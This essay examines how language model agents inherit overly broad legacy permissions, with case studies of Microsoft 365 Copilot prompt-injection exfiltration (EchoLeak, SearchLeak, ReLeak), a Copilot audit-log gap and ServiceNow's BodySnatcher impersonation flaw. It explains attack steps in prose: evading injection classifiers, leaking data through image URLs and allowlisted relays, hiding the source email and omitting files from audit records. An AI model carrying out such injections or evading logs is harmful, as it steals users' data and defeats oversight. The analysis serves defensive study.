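# Security and control risks of retrofitting language model agents onto legacy software permissions

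## How agents get permissions from software built for people

A language model agent is a program in which a language model pursues a goal by choosing and carrying out a series of actions through software tools. A system that finds a flight, checks the user's calendar and pays for the ticket is an agent, while a chatbot that only answers a question about flights is not. The agent needs permission to read the calendar and make the payment. Usually the only permissions available are ones that software companies designed years ago for human users or for scripts that repeat the same job every night. An agent that acts through such permissions is a retrofitted agent. Retrofitting is risky because these permissions cannot be limited to one action for one task, and the model can make mistakes or follow instructions in text it should not obey.

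Siu, He and colleagues (2026), in *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security*, give a compact description of how an agent runs. The user writes a prompt p. At each step t the model f produces an action a from the prompt, the trajectory Tr (the earlier actions and what came back from them) and the memory M that persists between tasks:

a_t ~ f( · | p, Tr_{t−1}, M_t )

The action is often a tool call, a request from the model to run a function with specific values, such as a file name or an account number. The running example is a cooking assistant. Its user wants a healthy dinner recipe and the ingredients for it, so the assistant searches a recipe database, asks the user to pick a dish, checks the pantry and places an order. The right-hand side of the formula is the important part for security, because the user's request and the text of a stranger's recipe blog end up in the same context,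 and the model chooses its next action based on all of it.

### Four ways of holding authority

The most familiar route is the "allow access" screen. When the user approves, the service issues an access token, a string that grants access to whoever presents it. The token's scopes, which are named permissions such as "read mail", limit that access. According to Notebookcheck's *ChatGPT connects two Google accounts, write access included*, OpenAI asks for a scope named gmail.modify when ChatGPT connects to Gmail. This scope covers reading, composing and sending mail across the account, and excludes only permanent deletion that skips the trash. A user who wants a summary of one thread therefore gives ChatGPT access to the whole mailbox and the ability to send mail from it. This is a coarse permission, meaning one that covers far more data or actions than a single task needs.

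Companies more often use a service account, which belongs to a program rather than a person. For example, when an assistant answers staff questions from the personnel database, the database receives every query from the same account, whichever employee asked. These accounts tend to get little attention. Sophos reported in 2026 that only 34% of organizations regularly audit or rotate their service accounts and other non-human identities. Sophos sells security products, so the figure deserves some caution.

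A stored key is an even cruder method. For example, an engineer pastes a database key into the settings of an agent that writes weekly sales reports, and a year later the key is still there and works for the agent and anyone else who copies it. Curity, an identity vendor, reports that in February 2026 researchers at the security firm Wiz found a key to a misconfigured database at Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, which gave them access to 35,000 email addresses and 1.5 million more keys.

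The last route is a logged-in browser session. ChatGPT's cloud browser, which runs on OpenAI's machines, stops at a login page and shows the user a form. A separate model checks for signs of phishing, the user types the password, and the password goes to the remote browser without passing through the agent's model. This protects the password, but OpenAI's *Using cloud browser in ChatGPT* explains that the login "will persist for future tasks until it expires". The login persists as a cookie, and Notebookcheck's *ChatGPT signs in to your accounts now and stays signed in* points out that such a cookie opens the account without the password or second factor. An agent that logged in on Monday to check a delivery date can still act in the shop's account on Thursday.

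OpenAI's dots, always-on agents introduced in September 2026 that keep working between conversations, routinely use delegated tokens and browser sessions. They can connect to more than 4,000 apps, according to OpenAI's Japanese launch post, *dots のご紹介* (2026). On December 2, OpenAI opened dots to the much cheaper Plus plan worldwide, as it announced in *Bringing dots to more people in ChatGPT*. The same day, dots became able to sign in to websites with a user's saved logins. The user approves a login once, not at every visit, according to Xcelcor's *ChatGPT dots can now sign in to websites for you* (2026).

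OpenAI's *Connecting and managing app accounts in ChatGPT* advises users to choose the account "that already has access to the information you need". OpenAI's *ChatGPT release notes* state that the business data plugin runs queries with the connected account's existing permissions. Reusing those permissions is sensible if no others are available, but the agent then starts with whatever access the person has accumulated over the years.

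### Why the old permissions are so broad

Broad permissions were a reasonable tradeoff when only people and fixed scripts used them. In *We Finally Measured How Broken Permissions Are*, Graham Neray, chief executive of the authorization company Oso, says human judgment and slowness kept the risk tolerable. An employee with access to a hundred systems could be fired for misusing it and works only so many hours a day. Companies left broad access in place because trimming it takes administrators time and sometimes blocks real work.

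Scripts, by contrast, were safe because their behavior was narrow. A nightly backup program may have access to the entire database, but its code is short, it does the same thing each time, and a reviewer can read it in advance. An agent that replaces the script has the same access, but its behavior depends on text that nobody has read yet.

In March 2026, Oso and the data security company Cyera published an attempt to measure how much access goes unused, covering 2.4 million workers and 3.6 billion application permissions over 90 days. Oso's *Least Privilege Research Report 2026* (2026) found that workers used 4% of the permissions they held. A permission here means a kind of action on a kind of resource, such as editing sales opportunities, so somebody who can read 500 records and opens one has used that permission in full. Oso gives the example of a sales manager who holds eight types of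 permission and, over the period, views 15 opportunities and edits 3, which counts as using two of the eight, or 25%. Because this count ignores how many records each permission covers, the companies measured data use separately and found that workers touched 9% of the sensitive data they could reach. They also found that 31% of workers could modify or delete sensitive data.

The companies use the 4% figure for two different claims. Cyera's *96% of Enterprise Permissions Go Unused* (2026) reports that only 4% of workers take any action in most applications, and that those workers use 17% of the permissions available to them. Oso's report includes that claim and also the claim that 4% of all permissions were used. The two claims do not obviously agree. If 4% of workers are active and each uses 17% of an average-sized set of permissions, then the share of all permissions in use is 0.04 × 0.17,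 or about 0.7%. For that share to be 4%, the active workers would have to hold nearly a quarter of all permissions. They may, since heavy users are often administrators, or the two figures may average over applications in different ways.

The 17% is probably the better number for agents. People connect agents to software they use, so the relevant permissions are the unused five-sixths in an active account, not those in accounts that nobody opens. But the 90-day window misses work done once a year, and the sample consists of companies that already pay for access-management tools, as Oso acknowledges. Both companies also sell products that address the problem. Oso's *The 96% Blind Spot* (2026), the press release for the study, describes Oso as "the agent permissions posture company", and Neray writes that he had bet his team on the outcome beforehand.

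More important, the study measured only people. Oso's comparison, in which an agent reads 100% of the reachable data in seconds, is labeled "illustrative". The study therefore supports the claim that an agent which inherits an employee's account inherits mostly excess permissions, and this claim would hold even if the percentages were far off. The study doesn't show how much of that excess access agents use.

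One way to try to restore human judgment is to ask the user to approve each action. Jaloza (2026), in *If you want a secure AI agent, start restricting its environment*, describes the tradeoff this creates at Microsoft, where human review makes an agent safer but less autonomous, and standing credentials make it more autonomous but less safe. Review also becomes less effective with repetition. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* (2026) reports that users of the company's coding agent approved roughly 93% of its permission prompts. That rate alone proves little, since most of the requests may have been fine, but Anthropic also found that the more prompts people see, the less attention they pay to each one. Agents are now taking many more actions, which weakens any safeguard that depends on users' attention.

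### How excess authority becomes harm

Prompt injection is text in material an agent reads that the model follows as if it were an instruction from its user. For text from outside sources, Siu and colleagues use a narrower definition. They count an injection only when the text that led to the action came from a source the system has not authenticated and the action does not serve the user's task. An agent may therefore follow an unauthenticated recipe page that says to bake at 350°F, because that serves the user's task. The second condition matters in practice because a filter that blocked every outside instruction would also block the recipe. An email that tells a summarizing agent to send all customer data to a stranger meets both conditions. EchoLeak, a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, allowed an attack of this kind.

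The combined formula from Siu and colleagues still has a gap, as one of their own examples shows. Suppose an agent buying ingredients reads a recipe page that includes the words "use payment method ending in 9876" and obeys. Siu and colleagues call this a violation because only the user should choose the card. Yet their formula excuses an outside instruction whenever the resulting action serves the task, and buying ingredients does, so it would allow this purchase. A useful permission check has to look at the values in the call, including which card is used, as well as whether the agent may buy groceries.

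An agent can cause harm without an attacker. The same cooking assistant might read that a dish works best in a certain pan and add a skillet to the cart, spending money its user never agreed to spend. OWASP, a software security foundation, calls this problem excessive agency in its list of top risks for language model applications. The term covers harm, with or without an attacker, that was possible because an agent had more functions, permissions or autonomy than its task needed. Curity describes a much more damaging case, in which a coding agent on a routine task deleted the production database of PocketOS, which supplies software to car rental businesses.

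The standard remedy is the principle of least privilege. In *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (1975), Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder argued that every program and every user should work with the smallest set of privileges the job requires, mainly to limit the damage from accidents and errors. Under this principle, an agent should hold only the authority its current task requires, and only for as long as the task requires it.

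Norm Hardy described a related failure in *The Confused Deputy* (1988). A compiler had permission to write in a system directory that held both its usage statistics and the billing records. Users could tell the compiler where to put its debugging output, and one of them gave the name of the billing file, which the compiler then overwrote. The user had no permission to write to that file, but the compiler did, because it needed to save its statistics in the same directory. The system did not link each write to the person the compiler was acting for. A confused deputy is a program that has some authority and is induced to use it by someone who lacks that authority.

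Siu and colleagues state the condition for agents exactly. Let R be the set of permitted pairs, so that (x, y) ∈ R means x may access y. A confused deputy attack occurs when an action reaches a target for a user and

(user, target) ∉ R, while (agent, target) ∈ R.

An agent can use its own access to reach a target for a user who isn't allowed to reach it. In the paper's example, an employee asks a company assistant for everyone's salaries. The employee has no access to the personnel database, but the assistant does, for administrative work, so it answers. Because the employee has logged in properly, a check that only confirms the user is genuine will pass the request. To catch it, the system has to check whether this particular user may access this particular target.

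An agent's exposure to the confused deputy problem depends on which of the four routes it uses to get permissions. Service accounts and stored keys create this risk because the agent's authority comes from somewhere other than the person asking. A delegated token mostly rules out the narrow version, in which the agent can reach something its user cannot, because it gives the agent only the user's access. But Hardy's idea also applies when the instructions come from someone other than the user. If an agent with a full mailbox token reads a malicious email from a stranger, the problem returns, because the agent can read the mailbox and the stranger cannot. Acting strictly as the user therefore stops employees from exceeding their own access through the agent, but it does not protect the user from strangers.

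### Products for agents and authorization for agents

A company can build a new product for agents and still run it on permissions that predate agents. Much of OpenAI's dots product, for example, is new. Each dot has its own cloud computer, and OpenAI's *How we build safety, security, and privacy into dots* (2026) describes custom rules that users can set and a separate check before a dot acts. In ChatGPT's app settings, a user can choose to approve everything, to approve only changes, or to let low-risk actions through. These controls operate on OpenAI's side. OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* states that the settings do not change access in the source system, and that changing them does not revoke access already granted to an account. If a user picks "always ask", ChatGPT's Gmail token can still read and send everything, so Google's servers will accept the call if OpenAI's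 control fails.

Agent-first authorization means permissions and checks designed for callers that are models and can be misled by untrusted text. Parts of the same product come close to this. With ChatGPT Wallet, which OpenAI introduced in November 2026, the user reviews the merchant, items, total and card before a dot pays, then confirms with a fingerprint or face scan. This review resembles per-call authorization, which checks before each tool call runs whether that call is allowed with those values. It would stop the skillet purchase if the user reads the list. The checkout also receives a substitute payment credential, so the agent never handles the real card number.

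A simpler change may also help. Ortiz (2026) reports in *Dots opens up* that OpenAI plans to give dots their own email addresses, so that a user can forward a specific thread. Forwarding gives the agent access to one thread, whereas connecting Gmail gives it access to the whole mailbox, though the model, the assistant and the task can be the same in both cases.

### Two tests

Range, duration and fit determine whether an agent has only the authority its task needs. Range is the data and actions the permission covers, compared with what the task requires. Duration is whether the authority ends when the task does. Fit is whether the permission allows the needed action but blocks harmful ones within the same range, such as allowing a reply to a landlord but not to a thief. The access token for a Gmail connection used to summarize one thread does badly on all three. It covers the whole mailbox,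 outlasts the task and, if its scope allows sending, allows sending to anyone. Approval prompts can improve fit, but they rely on the user's attention.

Auditability is the ability to establish from records what was done, by which person or agent, and in response to what. The records may not be enough for this if some steps were not recorded or if the records are split between companies. For example, Dots have an activity view where the user can open a task and look at each step, but OpenAI keeps that record, and the mail provider or the shop keeps its own.

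Records may also fail to distinguish the agent from the person, because an action the agent takes in a user's session ordinarily looks like the user's own. There has been some progress on this problem. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Work's Cloud browser allowlisting* explains that the cloud browser signs its requests, so a website that checks the signatures can confirm that the traffic came from ChatGPT. The signature identifies the service but not the task the agent was working on.

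The hardest thing to recover is what prompted the action. Siu and colleagues define one function that picks out which inputs acted as instructions for a given action, and another that traces each input to its source. They present both as ideals because the output of the first has to be inferred from the workings of a neural network, which real systems can only do approximately. A good log can show that the agent read a stranger's email and, one step later, forwarded a contract. An investigator would conclude that the email prompted the forwarding, and would usually be right, but the log shows only the order of events.

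## Microsoft 365 Copilot: an assistant with all of its user's access

Microsoft 365 Copilot is the assistant built into Word, Outlook, Teams and Microsoft's other office programs. It answers a question such as "What did we promise this client?" by searching the employee's mail, files and chats and writing a reply from what it finds. Copilot is a retrofitted agent because Microsoft ran it on the permission system that customers already used for people. It is also fairly limited as an agent. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), a case study of Copilot's best-known flaw, points out that it could not send email on its own. Security researchers nevertheless got confidential data out of it in 2025, and again several times in 2026, without defeating the access rules on that data.

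### How Copilot finds its material

Copilot searches for material through Microsoft Graph, the interface programs use to access an organization's Microsoft 365 data. The search can cover the employee's mailbox, personal and shared files, internal websites and Teams chats. Copilot puts the passages that look most relevant into the model's context with the question, and the model writes its answer from them. This is called retrieval-augmented generation.

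Copilot searches with the signed-in user's permissions. According to Microsoft's documentation, it "only surfaces organizational data to which individual users have at least view permissions", and the search index applies the same limit. Collab365's *Microsoft details what Copilot can access and retain* reports that the version Microsoft updated on August 18, 2026 still contains this assurance.

Microsoft can reasonably describe this design as respecting permissions. The salary request that works on an assistant with a broad service account fails here, because Copilot searches with the employee's own rights and finds nothing the employee could not already open. Administrators also avoid maintaining a second set of permissions, which would soon stop matching the first.

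Microsoft itself discusses the problem of oversharing. Suppose somebody shares a salary spreadsheet with the whole company by mistake. It may do no harm for years because nobody knows it is there, but Copilot can find it for anyone who asks about pay. Microsoft therefore tells administrators to reduce accidental sharing, clean up unused sites and make sure every site has an owner. This advice is useful when employees have access they shouldn't have, but EchoLeak worked on data that the employee was entitled to read.

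### EchoLeak

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) was a vulnerability that let an outsider send an employee one email and later receive confidential data from Copilot. Researchers at Aim Security, a startup, found it in January 2025 and published it on June 11, after Microsoft had fixed it. Their account, *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025), calls it "zero-click" because the employee did not have to open the email or click on anything in it. The employee did have to ask Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the email, which most users would do sooner or later.

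The attack had to get past a series of safeguards, and Microsoft had put some thought into them.

Microsoft's first defense was a classifier meant to detect text containing instructions for the assistant and keep that text away from the model. The researchers wrote their email as a request to the employee, without mentioning AI or Copilot, and the classifier didn't block it. This is hard to fix with a better classifier because ordinary office mail is full of instructions. "Please pull together the latest figures" is harmless when a colleague sends it to a person, but the wording doesn't show whether a person or the assistant will act on it.

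Copilot retrieves text that resembles the user's question, so an email on one subject would rarely reach the model. The researchers therefore wrote a long email with sections on common office subjects, such as onboarding and leave, and Copilot retrieved it for questions on various topics. Copilot then placed this outside text in the same context as internal documents, which Reddy and Gujral identify as the point where the design violated least privilege.

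The model followed the email's instruction to pick out sensitive information from the other material in its context. Ravia calls this an "LLM scope violation", in which text from an untrusted source makes the model use trusted data without the user's explicit consent.

The attacker still needed a way to send the data out. Copilot removed links to outside websites from its answers, but its filter recognized only the usual way of writing a link and missed a valid alternative. The user would have had to click a link, so the researchers used an image instead. A browser requests an image as soon as it displays the page, and the image's address can carry data.

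The remaining barrier was the content security policy on Copilot's page, which lists the sites from which the browser may load content. The attacker's server was not on the list, but several Microsoft services were, including a Teams service that would fetch an outside address on request. The browser sent its request to that service, which then contacted the attacker's server.

The email also contained an instruction not to mention it, so Copilot's answer did not cite the email that had influenced it. An employee who noticed something odd in the answer would have had nothing to connect it to the email.

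Ravia says that the attack could take anything in Copilot's context, including the chat history, the retrieved documents and details such as the user's name. This is less than everything the employee could open. If U is the set of items the user may read, C the contents of the context and L what leaks, then

L ⊆ C ⊆ U.

Copilot's permission check guarantees the second relation, that the user is allowed to read everything that enters the context. The check does not affect how large L is or who receives it.

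Microsoft needed several months to fix the vulnerability. Goldman (2025), in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*, reports that the company attempted a fix in April and found further problems in May. Customers had nothing to install, since Copilot runs on Microsoft's servers. Aim's researchers knew of no administrator setting that would have prevented the attack.

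### Why the permission check had nothing to refuse

Siu and colleagues' condition for a confused deputy requires that the user may not access the target while the agent may. EchoLeak does not meet it. For every item that Copilot read,

(user, target) ∈ R and (agent, target) ∈ R.

The user was genuine, had signed in properly and had permission to read each document. A correct check of the user's permissions on each document must therefore approve all of these reads.

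The condition does hold if the sender of the email takes the user's place:

(sender, target) ∉ R, while (agent, target) ∈ R.

This is the more sensible way to apply it, because the sender's instruction led to the disclosure. Ravia makes the same point with a comparison from Unix, where some programs run with their owner's privileges no matter who starts them. The email resembles an unprivileged program that uses one of these programs to open files it could not open itself.

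Microsoft's permission system could not apply the second version because it had no value to use for the sender. The system was designed for people, and when a person opens a file, the account making the request almost always belongs to the person who wants the file. When a language model opens a file, the request comes from the employee's account, but any text in the model's context may have prompted it. A user-level permission check uses only the account, so it cannot determine whose instruction the model is following. Making the check stricter doesn't help because it still lacks that information.

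*ConfusedPilot* (2024) had already compared Copilot to the confused deputy, but the attacker in that paper is an untrusted employee who tries to corrupt the answers that Copilot gives to colleagues. With EchoLeak, an attacker outside the company could steal data.

The check also did not cover where the data was sent. Permission to read a contract does not include permission to send it to strangers, but older systems left that decision to the employee's judgment. The developer and blogger Willison (2025) describes EchoLeak as another case of a pattern already seen in a dozen products. The pattern requires private data, exposure to malicious text and a way to send data out. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes nearly the same condition, in which untrusted text controls a program that can retrieve confidential data and send it anywhere.

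Removing any one of the three conditions would stop the attack. Companies buy Copilot for its access to private data, so that access has to stay. Reddy and Gujral instead propose limiting its exposure to malicious text by having it answer from internal sources by default and use outside email only when the user asks for it. They write that EchoLeak then "fails by design".

I would expect this to help, but it costs more than it first seems to.

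A salesperson who asks Copilot to compare a client's latest email with the company's price list needs both sources in one answer. Reddy and Gujral also ran no experiments to test the proposal, and they rate it as failing against zero-click data theft in their own matrix of defenses. Designs that track where each piece of data came from, such as CaMeL, are meant to let an agent read outside text without letting that text control where data goes.

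The remaining defense is to block the routes by which data can leave. Microsoft had already tried this with the link filter and the browser's list of approved sites, but its later record shows how hard it is to find every route.

### SearchLeak and the flaws that followed

In June 2026, a year after EchoLeak, the security company Varonis published *SearchLeak*, which describes another way to get data out of Copilot. The attack, catalogued as CVE-2026-42824, requires one click on a link to a real Microsoft address.

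The link contained text for Copilot's search box, and the search page passed that text to the model. The model followed it as an instruction to search the employee's mail and put what it found into the address of an image. Microsoft had a safeguard that turned such images into harmless text, but it ran only after the model had finished writing. The browser displayed the answer as it arrived, so it requested the image before the safeguard took effect. The request went to Bing, which was on the list of approved sites, and Bing's image search servers then fetched the attacker's address.

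The last stage is very close to EchoLeak's. In both attacks, an image request carried the data, and a Microsoft service on the approved list relayed it. Microsoft had closed the route through Teams, but an equivalent route through Bing was still open. Copilot's authority had not changed either. Varonis writes that Copilot works with the user's full Graph permissions, so the attacker in effect inherits the victim's access. Varonis's example took only the subject line of one email, but a subject line can contain a login code.

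SearchLeak also shows a limit of the remedy that Reddy and Gujral propose. A rule against outside email would not have stopped it, because no email had to enter the context. The attacker's text came from a link and was entered as the user's own question. Even a system that carefully tracked sources would have attributed that text to the user, unless its designers had made it treat text from links as outside text.

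In August 2026 Varonis disclosed CoSnitch, an attack that used malicious links and planted false entries in Copilot's persistent memory, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*. On December 3, Cato AI Labs, the successor to Aim's research team, disclosed three more zero-click attacks under the name ReLeak. All three began with an unread email, as EchoLeak had. According to AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), the attacks got data out through an image address, a link to a saved file, and code that Copilot ran in an isolated environment. Microsoft had documented this environment as blocking outbound traffic, but the code could still send data out. Microsoft had patched the three attacks on September 17, November 11 and November 15.

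The fixes therefore seem to have closed individual attack routes without removing the class of flaw. The researchers take the same view, and *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) quotes them as saying that "too little progress has been made".

Two security companies found all of these attacks. Both sell protection against such attacks, so the number of discoveries partly reflects how hard they looked and is a poor guide to how many attack routes remain. But the new attacks worked, and a fix for the whole class would have stopped them however long the researchers searched. Other catalogue entries add little. For example, STAR Labs' *CVE-2025-59252* (2025) lists another Copilot disclosure flaw with a score of 9.3 but does not explain how the flaw worked, so it may have had a different cause.

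### Severity scores and signs of exploitation

Microsoft and the US National Vulnerability Database (NVD) scored both flaws on the Common Vulnerability Scoring System (CVSS), which runs from 0 to 10. Microsoft scored one flaw higher than the NVD did and the other lower.

| Flaw | Microsoft's score | NVD's score | Where the ratings differ |
|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | 9.3 | 7.5 | Whether the harm spreads beyond the flawed component, and whether the attacker can alter data |
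| SearchLeak | 6.5 | 7.5 | Whether the victim has to do anything |

GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) gives the ratings behind the two EchoLeak scores. Microsoft judged that the flaw affects resources under a different security authority, which CVSS calls a change of "scope", while NVD judged that it does not. Under the CVSS formula, that difference alone raises the score from 7.5 to 8.6. The rest of the gap comes from a slight risk of altered data, which only Microsoft counted. The disagreement over scope is understandable in a retrofitted system, because Copilot and the mailbox look like one system if judged by the user's rights, but like two if Copilot is treated as a separate program that a stranger has taken over.

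Microsoft scored SearchLeak as requiring a click from the user, while NVD scored it as requiring none. The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026) reports both scores. Microsoft's lower score fits the attack better, since Varonis's own description includes a click. Microsoft still gave SearchLeak its top severity label, "Critical". Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026) classifies the flaw as command injection, while STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-42824* (2026) describes it as missing authentication. Neither term covers a properly authenticated assistant that follows an attacker's instructions.

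Nobody has reported an attack on a real customer in either case. Microsoft said that EchoLeak affected no customers, and the US cybersecurity agency CISA had recorded no exploitation as of June 14, 2025. Microsoft also lists SearchLeak as not exploited. Cato knows of no attacks using ReLeak.

These statements are probably right. Goldman reports that Aim's team spent about three months reverse-engineering Copilot before it found EchoLeak, so few attackers are likely to have found it earlier. But customers would have had trouble checking for themselves, because the suspicious traffic went to Microsoft's own services and Copilot's answer did not mention the email. The assurance that nobody exploited EchoLeak therefore rests mostly on what Microsoft could see in its own systems. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* describes an even less visible attack, ShadowLeak,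 on ChatGPT's research agent. In that attack, the request left from the provider's servers and could be absent from the customer's monitoring.

### When Copilot ignored the confidential label

Companies can give Copilot less access than its user has. An administrator can write a data loss prevention policy meant to keep Copilot from processing any email or document with a certain label, such as "Confidential". The employee can still open a labeled message, but Copilot is not supposed to use its contents.

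In early 2026 this control failed, with no attacker involved. Customers reported on January 21 that Copilot Chat was summarizing labeled emails despite such policies. Microsoft issued advisory CW1226324 on February 3. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Code Error Allowed Copilot Chat to Expose Confidential Information* (2026) reports that Microsoft blamed a "code issue" that let Copilot pick up items in the Sent Items and Drafts folders. Other folders seemed unaffected. Microsoft was rolling out a fix by February 10.

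The same article describes the intended behavior. Its author labeled a message about an invented "Project Bunny" and asked Copilot about the project after the fix arrived. Copilot replied that it had found an internal reference but could not disclose the contents, so even when the policy works, Copilot can reveal that a protected message exists.

Microsoft responded to the criticism by saying that the error "did not provide anyone access to information they weren't already authorized to see". In the full statement, published in ITPro's *Microsoft Copilot bug saw AI snoop on confidential emails*, Microsoft added that access controls and data protection policies "remained intact" but that the behavior was not intended.

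The first claim is very likely true. The messages were in the user's own folders, and Microsoft says the user had written them, so no employee learned a colleague's secrets this way. But administrators had used the policy to keep certain text away from Copilot, and Copilot processed that text anyway. Microsoft judged the failure by the user's permissions, although the policy that failed was a limit on the agent.

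The claim that the policies remained intact is harder to accept, because although the settings may not have changed, Copilot did not enforce them for two folders. Missing Sent Items matters because it holds much of what a person has written to clients, lawyers and managers. TechRadar's *Microsoft admits an Office bug exposed confidential user emails to Copilot* adds that sent threads presumably include the incoming messages.

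EchoLeak shows why the difference between the user's and the agent's access matters. An email that takes over the model can't reach anything that stays out of Copilot's context. While the label failed, confidential sent mail could enter the context, so a working injection could have reached it, though no one has reported that this happened.

### The missing entries in the audit log

On July 4, 2025, Zack Korman of the security company Pistachio was testing a product feature that relied on Microsoft's audit log, which companies use to establish who opened which file. He noticed that Copilot sometimes summarized a file without the log showing it. He explains in Pistachio's *Copilot Broke Your Audit Log, but Microsoft Won’t Tell You* that he could then cause this on purpose, just by asking Copilot to summarize a file and not link to it.

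This worked on any file the user could open, including files the user had never opened through Copilot. An employee about to join a competitor could have gone through the company's plans this way and left no record of which ones. Doing so required no technical skill. The gap also appeared by chance, so honest employees may have produced incomplete records without knowing it.

Microsoft's log distinguishes Copilot's file access from a person's. When an employee opens a document directly, the log records a file-access entry, but when Copilot reads it for the employee, the log records a CopilotInteraction entry, which is supposed to list the files involved. Korman thinks this is the right design because recording that the employee had opened the file would be misleading.

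Korman describes the resulting log as empty. Office 365 for IT Pros' *Microsoft Fixes Copilot Audit Records* describes a narrower failure, in which the entry for the interaction omitted the file's name. Either way, an investigator searching for that file would not have found the access.

Microsoft probably built the log's list of files from the references in Copilot's answer rather than from what Copilot had read. Microsoft hasn't confirmed this, but it would explain why removing the link also removed the record. If so, the contents of a security log depended on how Copilot worded its reply, and anyone who could influence that wording could affect what was logged.

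EchoLeak's email included this kind of request, an instruction to the reader not to refer to the email. Korman tested files, not emails, so it isn't clear whether the same gap would have hidden the malicious message. But it might have, which is another reason to be cautious about using customers' logs from that period to rule out an attack.

Korman reported the problem to Microsoft at once. By July 10 Copilot's behavior had started to change, and Microsoft told him that the full fix would arrive on August 17. Office 365 for IT Pros later tested the fix by asking Copilot to summarize a document without linking to it, and this time the audit record listed the files.

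Michael Bargury, chief technology officer of the security company Zenity, had disclosed the gap about a year before Korman found it, but Microsoft had not fixed it. The log may therefore have been unreliable for a year or more.

Microsoft rated the flaw "important", one step below "critical", and so did not assign it a CVE number. It also noted that customers had nothing to install. On August 14 it told Korman that it had no plans to notify them. This reasoning doesn't suit a flaw in an audit log, because the fix made later entries complete but did not restore the missing ones. With an ordinary bug in a hosted service, the problem ends once the provider fixes its servers. Companies keep audit logs to consult later, and a hospital that relies on the log to show who viewed patient files would need to know that some of last year's entries may be missing.

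Such a hospital might recover some of the missing information from other records. Microsoft also stores users' prompts and Copilot's responses, so an investigator could search for requests to leave out links. That search would find people who hid their access deliberately, but it would miss the cases that Korman says occurred by chance. Nobody would think to run it without knowing about the gap.

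### Copilot on the two tests

Copilot does poorly on least privilege. A question about parental leave needs one personnel document, but Copilot can search everything the employee can read. Only relevance ranking narrows the search for a particular question, and it is not a security control. Attackers can exploit it, as EchoLeak did with an email written to rank well. Copilot also keeps the same access from one question to the next. Labels and site restrictions can limit what it searches, but only for all tasks at once.

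Microsoft's limits on what Copilot could do were useful, because an assistant that cannot send email or delete files can do less damage. But the researchers found a way to send data out through the display of an answer, so a list of Copilot's official functions understated what an attacker could do with it. Describing an agent that reads private data as "read-only" is safe only if its output can reach no one but the user.

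Auditability is better, at least since August 2025. The log identifies the user, marks the access as Copilot's and lists the files. A separate identity for Copilot would also let administrators assign it its own permissions. But even a complete log entry for an EchoLeak attack would look like the entry for an ordinary question about a client, because both would show an employee's question and the several internal documents and one outside email that Copilot read to answer it.

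## ServiceNow: AI agents behind an older chatbot interface

ServiceNow sells software that large organizations use to run internal services. Employees use it to report a broken laptop, ask for access to a system or change a benefits plan. According to ThaiCERT's *Critical AI-Driven Vulnerability Discovered in ServiceNow Could Lead to Full System Compromise* (2026), 85% of Fortune 500 companies are customers. In January 2026 the security company AppOmni described a flaw it called BodySnatcher (CVE-2025-12420), which let a stranger who knew an administrator's email address gain an administrator account. The attacker could then send the agent a plain request from the administrator's account, whereas EchoLeak relied on instructions hidden in material that Copilot read.

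### The chatbot before the agents

ServiceNow's older chatbot, Virtual Agent, identifies what a user wants and starts a matching "topic", a workflow that a developer wrote in advance for a task such as resetting a password or filing a ticket. Despite its name, Virtual Agent is not a language model agent. AppOmni points out that a topic can only follow the paths its developer defined.

Companies wanted their employees to reach the chatbot from Slack or Microsoft Teams, so ServiceNow offered an interface for outside chat tools. Chen, a ServiceNow employee, explains that the interface first authenticates the chat tool and then identifies the user. The tool can authenticate with a static secret, in effect a password. Under the instructions in ServiceNow's *Configure Message Authentication for inbound communication*, each customer creates its own secret. To identify the user, the tool sends an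 email address with the message, and ServiceNow links the conversation to the account with that address. According to ServiceNow's *Account linking in pre-built messaging integrations*, this happens without a prompt to the user. Without this link, ServiceNow treats everyone who writes through the interface as a guest.

This was a reasonable design for a chatbot. Slack has usually made the employee log in already, and a second login for every question about a laptop would drive people away. But ServiceNow verifies only the tool's identity and accepts whatever address the tool supplies, so anyone who obtains the secret can claim to be any employee. An impostor could do little while the interface led only to fixed workflows.

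### One secret for every customer

ServiceNow later added Now Assist, a set of AI features that includes agents. To let other companies' agents hand work to its own, ServiceNow reused the chatbot's interface and supplied new connections to it.

These connections came with the same secret on every customer's system, and the secret never changed. They also accepted an email address alone as proof of identity. Anyone who learned the secret could therefore start a conversation on any customer's system that had the connections switched on, posing as any employee whose address they knew. The customer's single sign-on and multi-factor authentication did not prevent this, because the conversation never passed through the login page.

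AppOmni nevertheless judged the risk of these flaws alone to be "relatively minimal". The most harmful thing Aaron Costello, the AppOmni researcher who found them, could do with them was send the human support desk a message that seemed to come from an administrator and asked for a new account for a contractor. Even this was awkward, because replies went to a preset address that the attacker did not control, so the support desk would get no sensible answer to any question it asked. AppOmni's judgment seems fair for the standard product, although the risk would have been greater for a customer whose own workflows did something drastic in a single step.

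### From an email address to an administrator account

ServiceNow had built a separate entrance for outside agents that required a ServiceNow account. But this entrance only converted each request to the older interface's format and put it in the chatbot's queue, where an internal topic started the agent. Costello found that a request in the same format, sent directly to the older interface, also started the agent.

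Any active agent would run if the user had the necessary permissions, even if nobody had used the agent for months. Administrators had generally assumed that an agent could run only in a channel where somebody had deployed it.

ServiceNow supplied an example agent that was active on every system with the product. It managed records, and one of its tools could create a record in any table. ServiceNow keeps user accounts in one table and their roles in another. Posing as an administrator, Costello told the agent to create a user and give it the administrator role. He then set the new user's password through the ordinary "forgot password" page and logged in.

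Assigning the role required the new account's internal identifier, which appeared only in replies that Costello could not see. A fixed workflow would probably have stopped there. Costello asked the agent to create the account and assign the role in a single instruction, and the agent carried the identifier from the first step to the second by itself.

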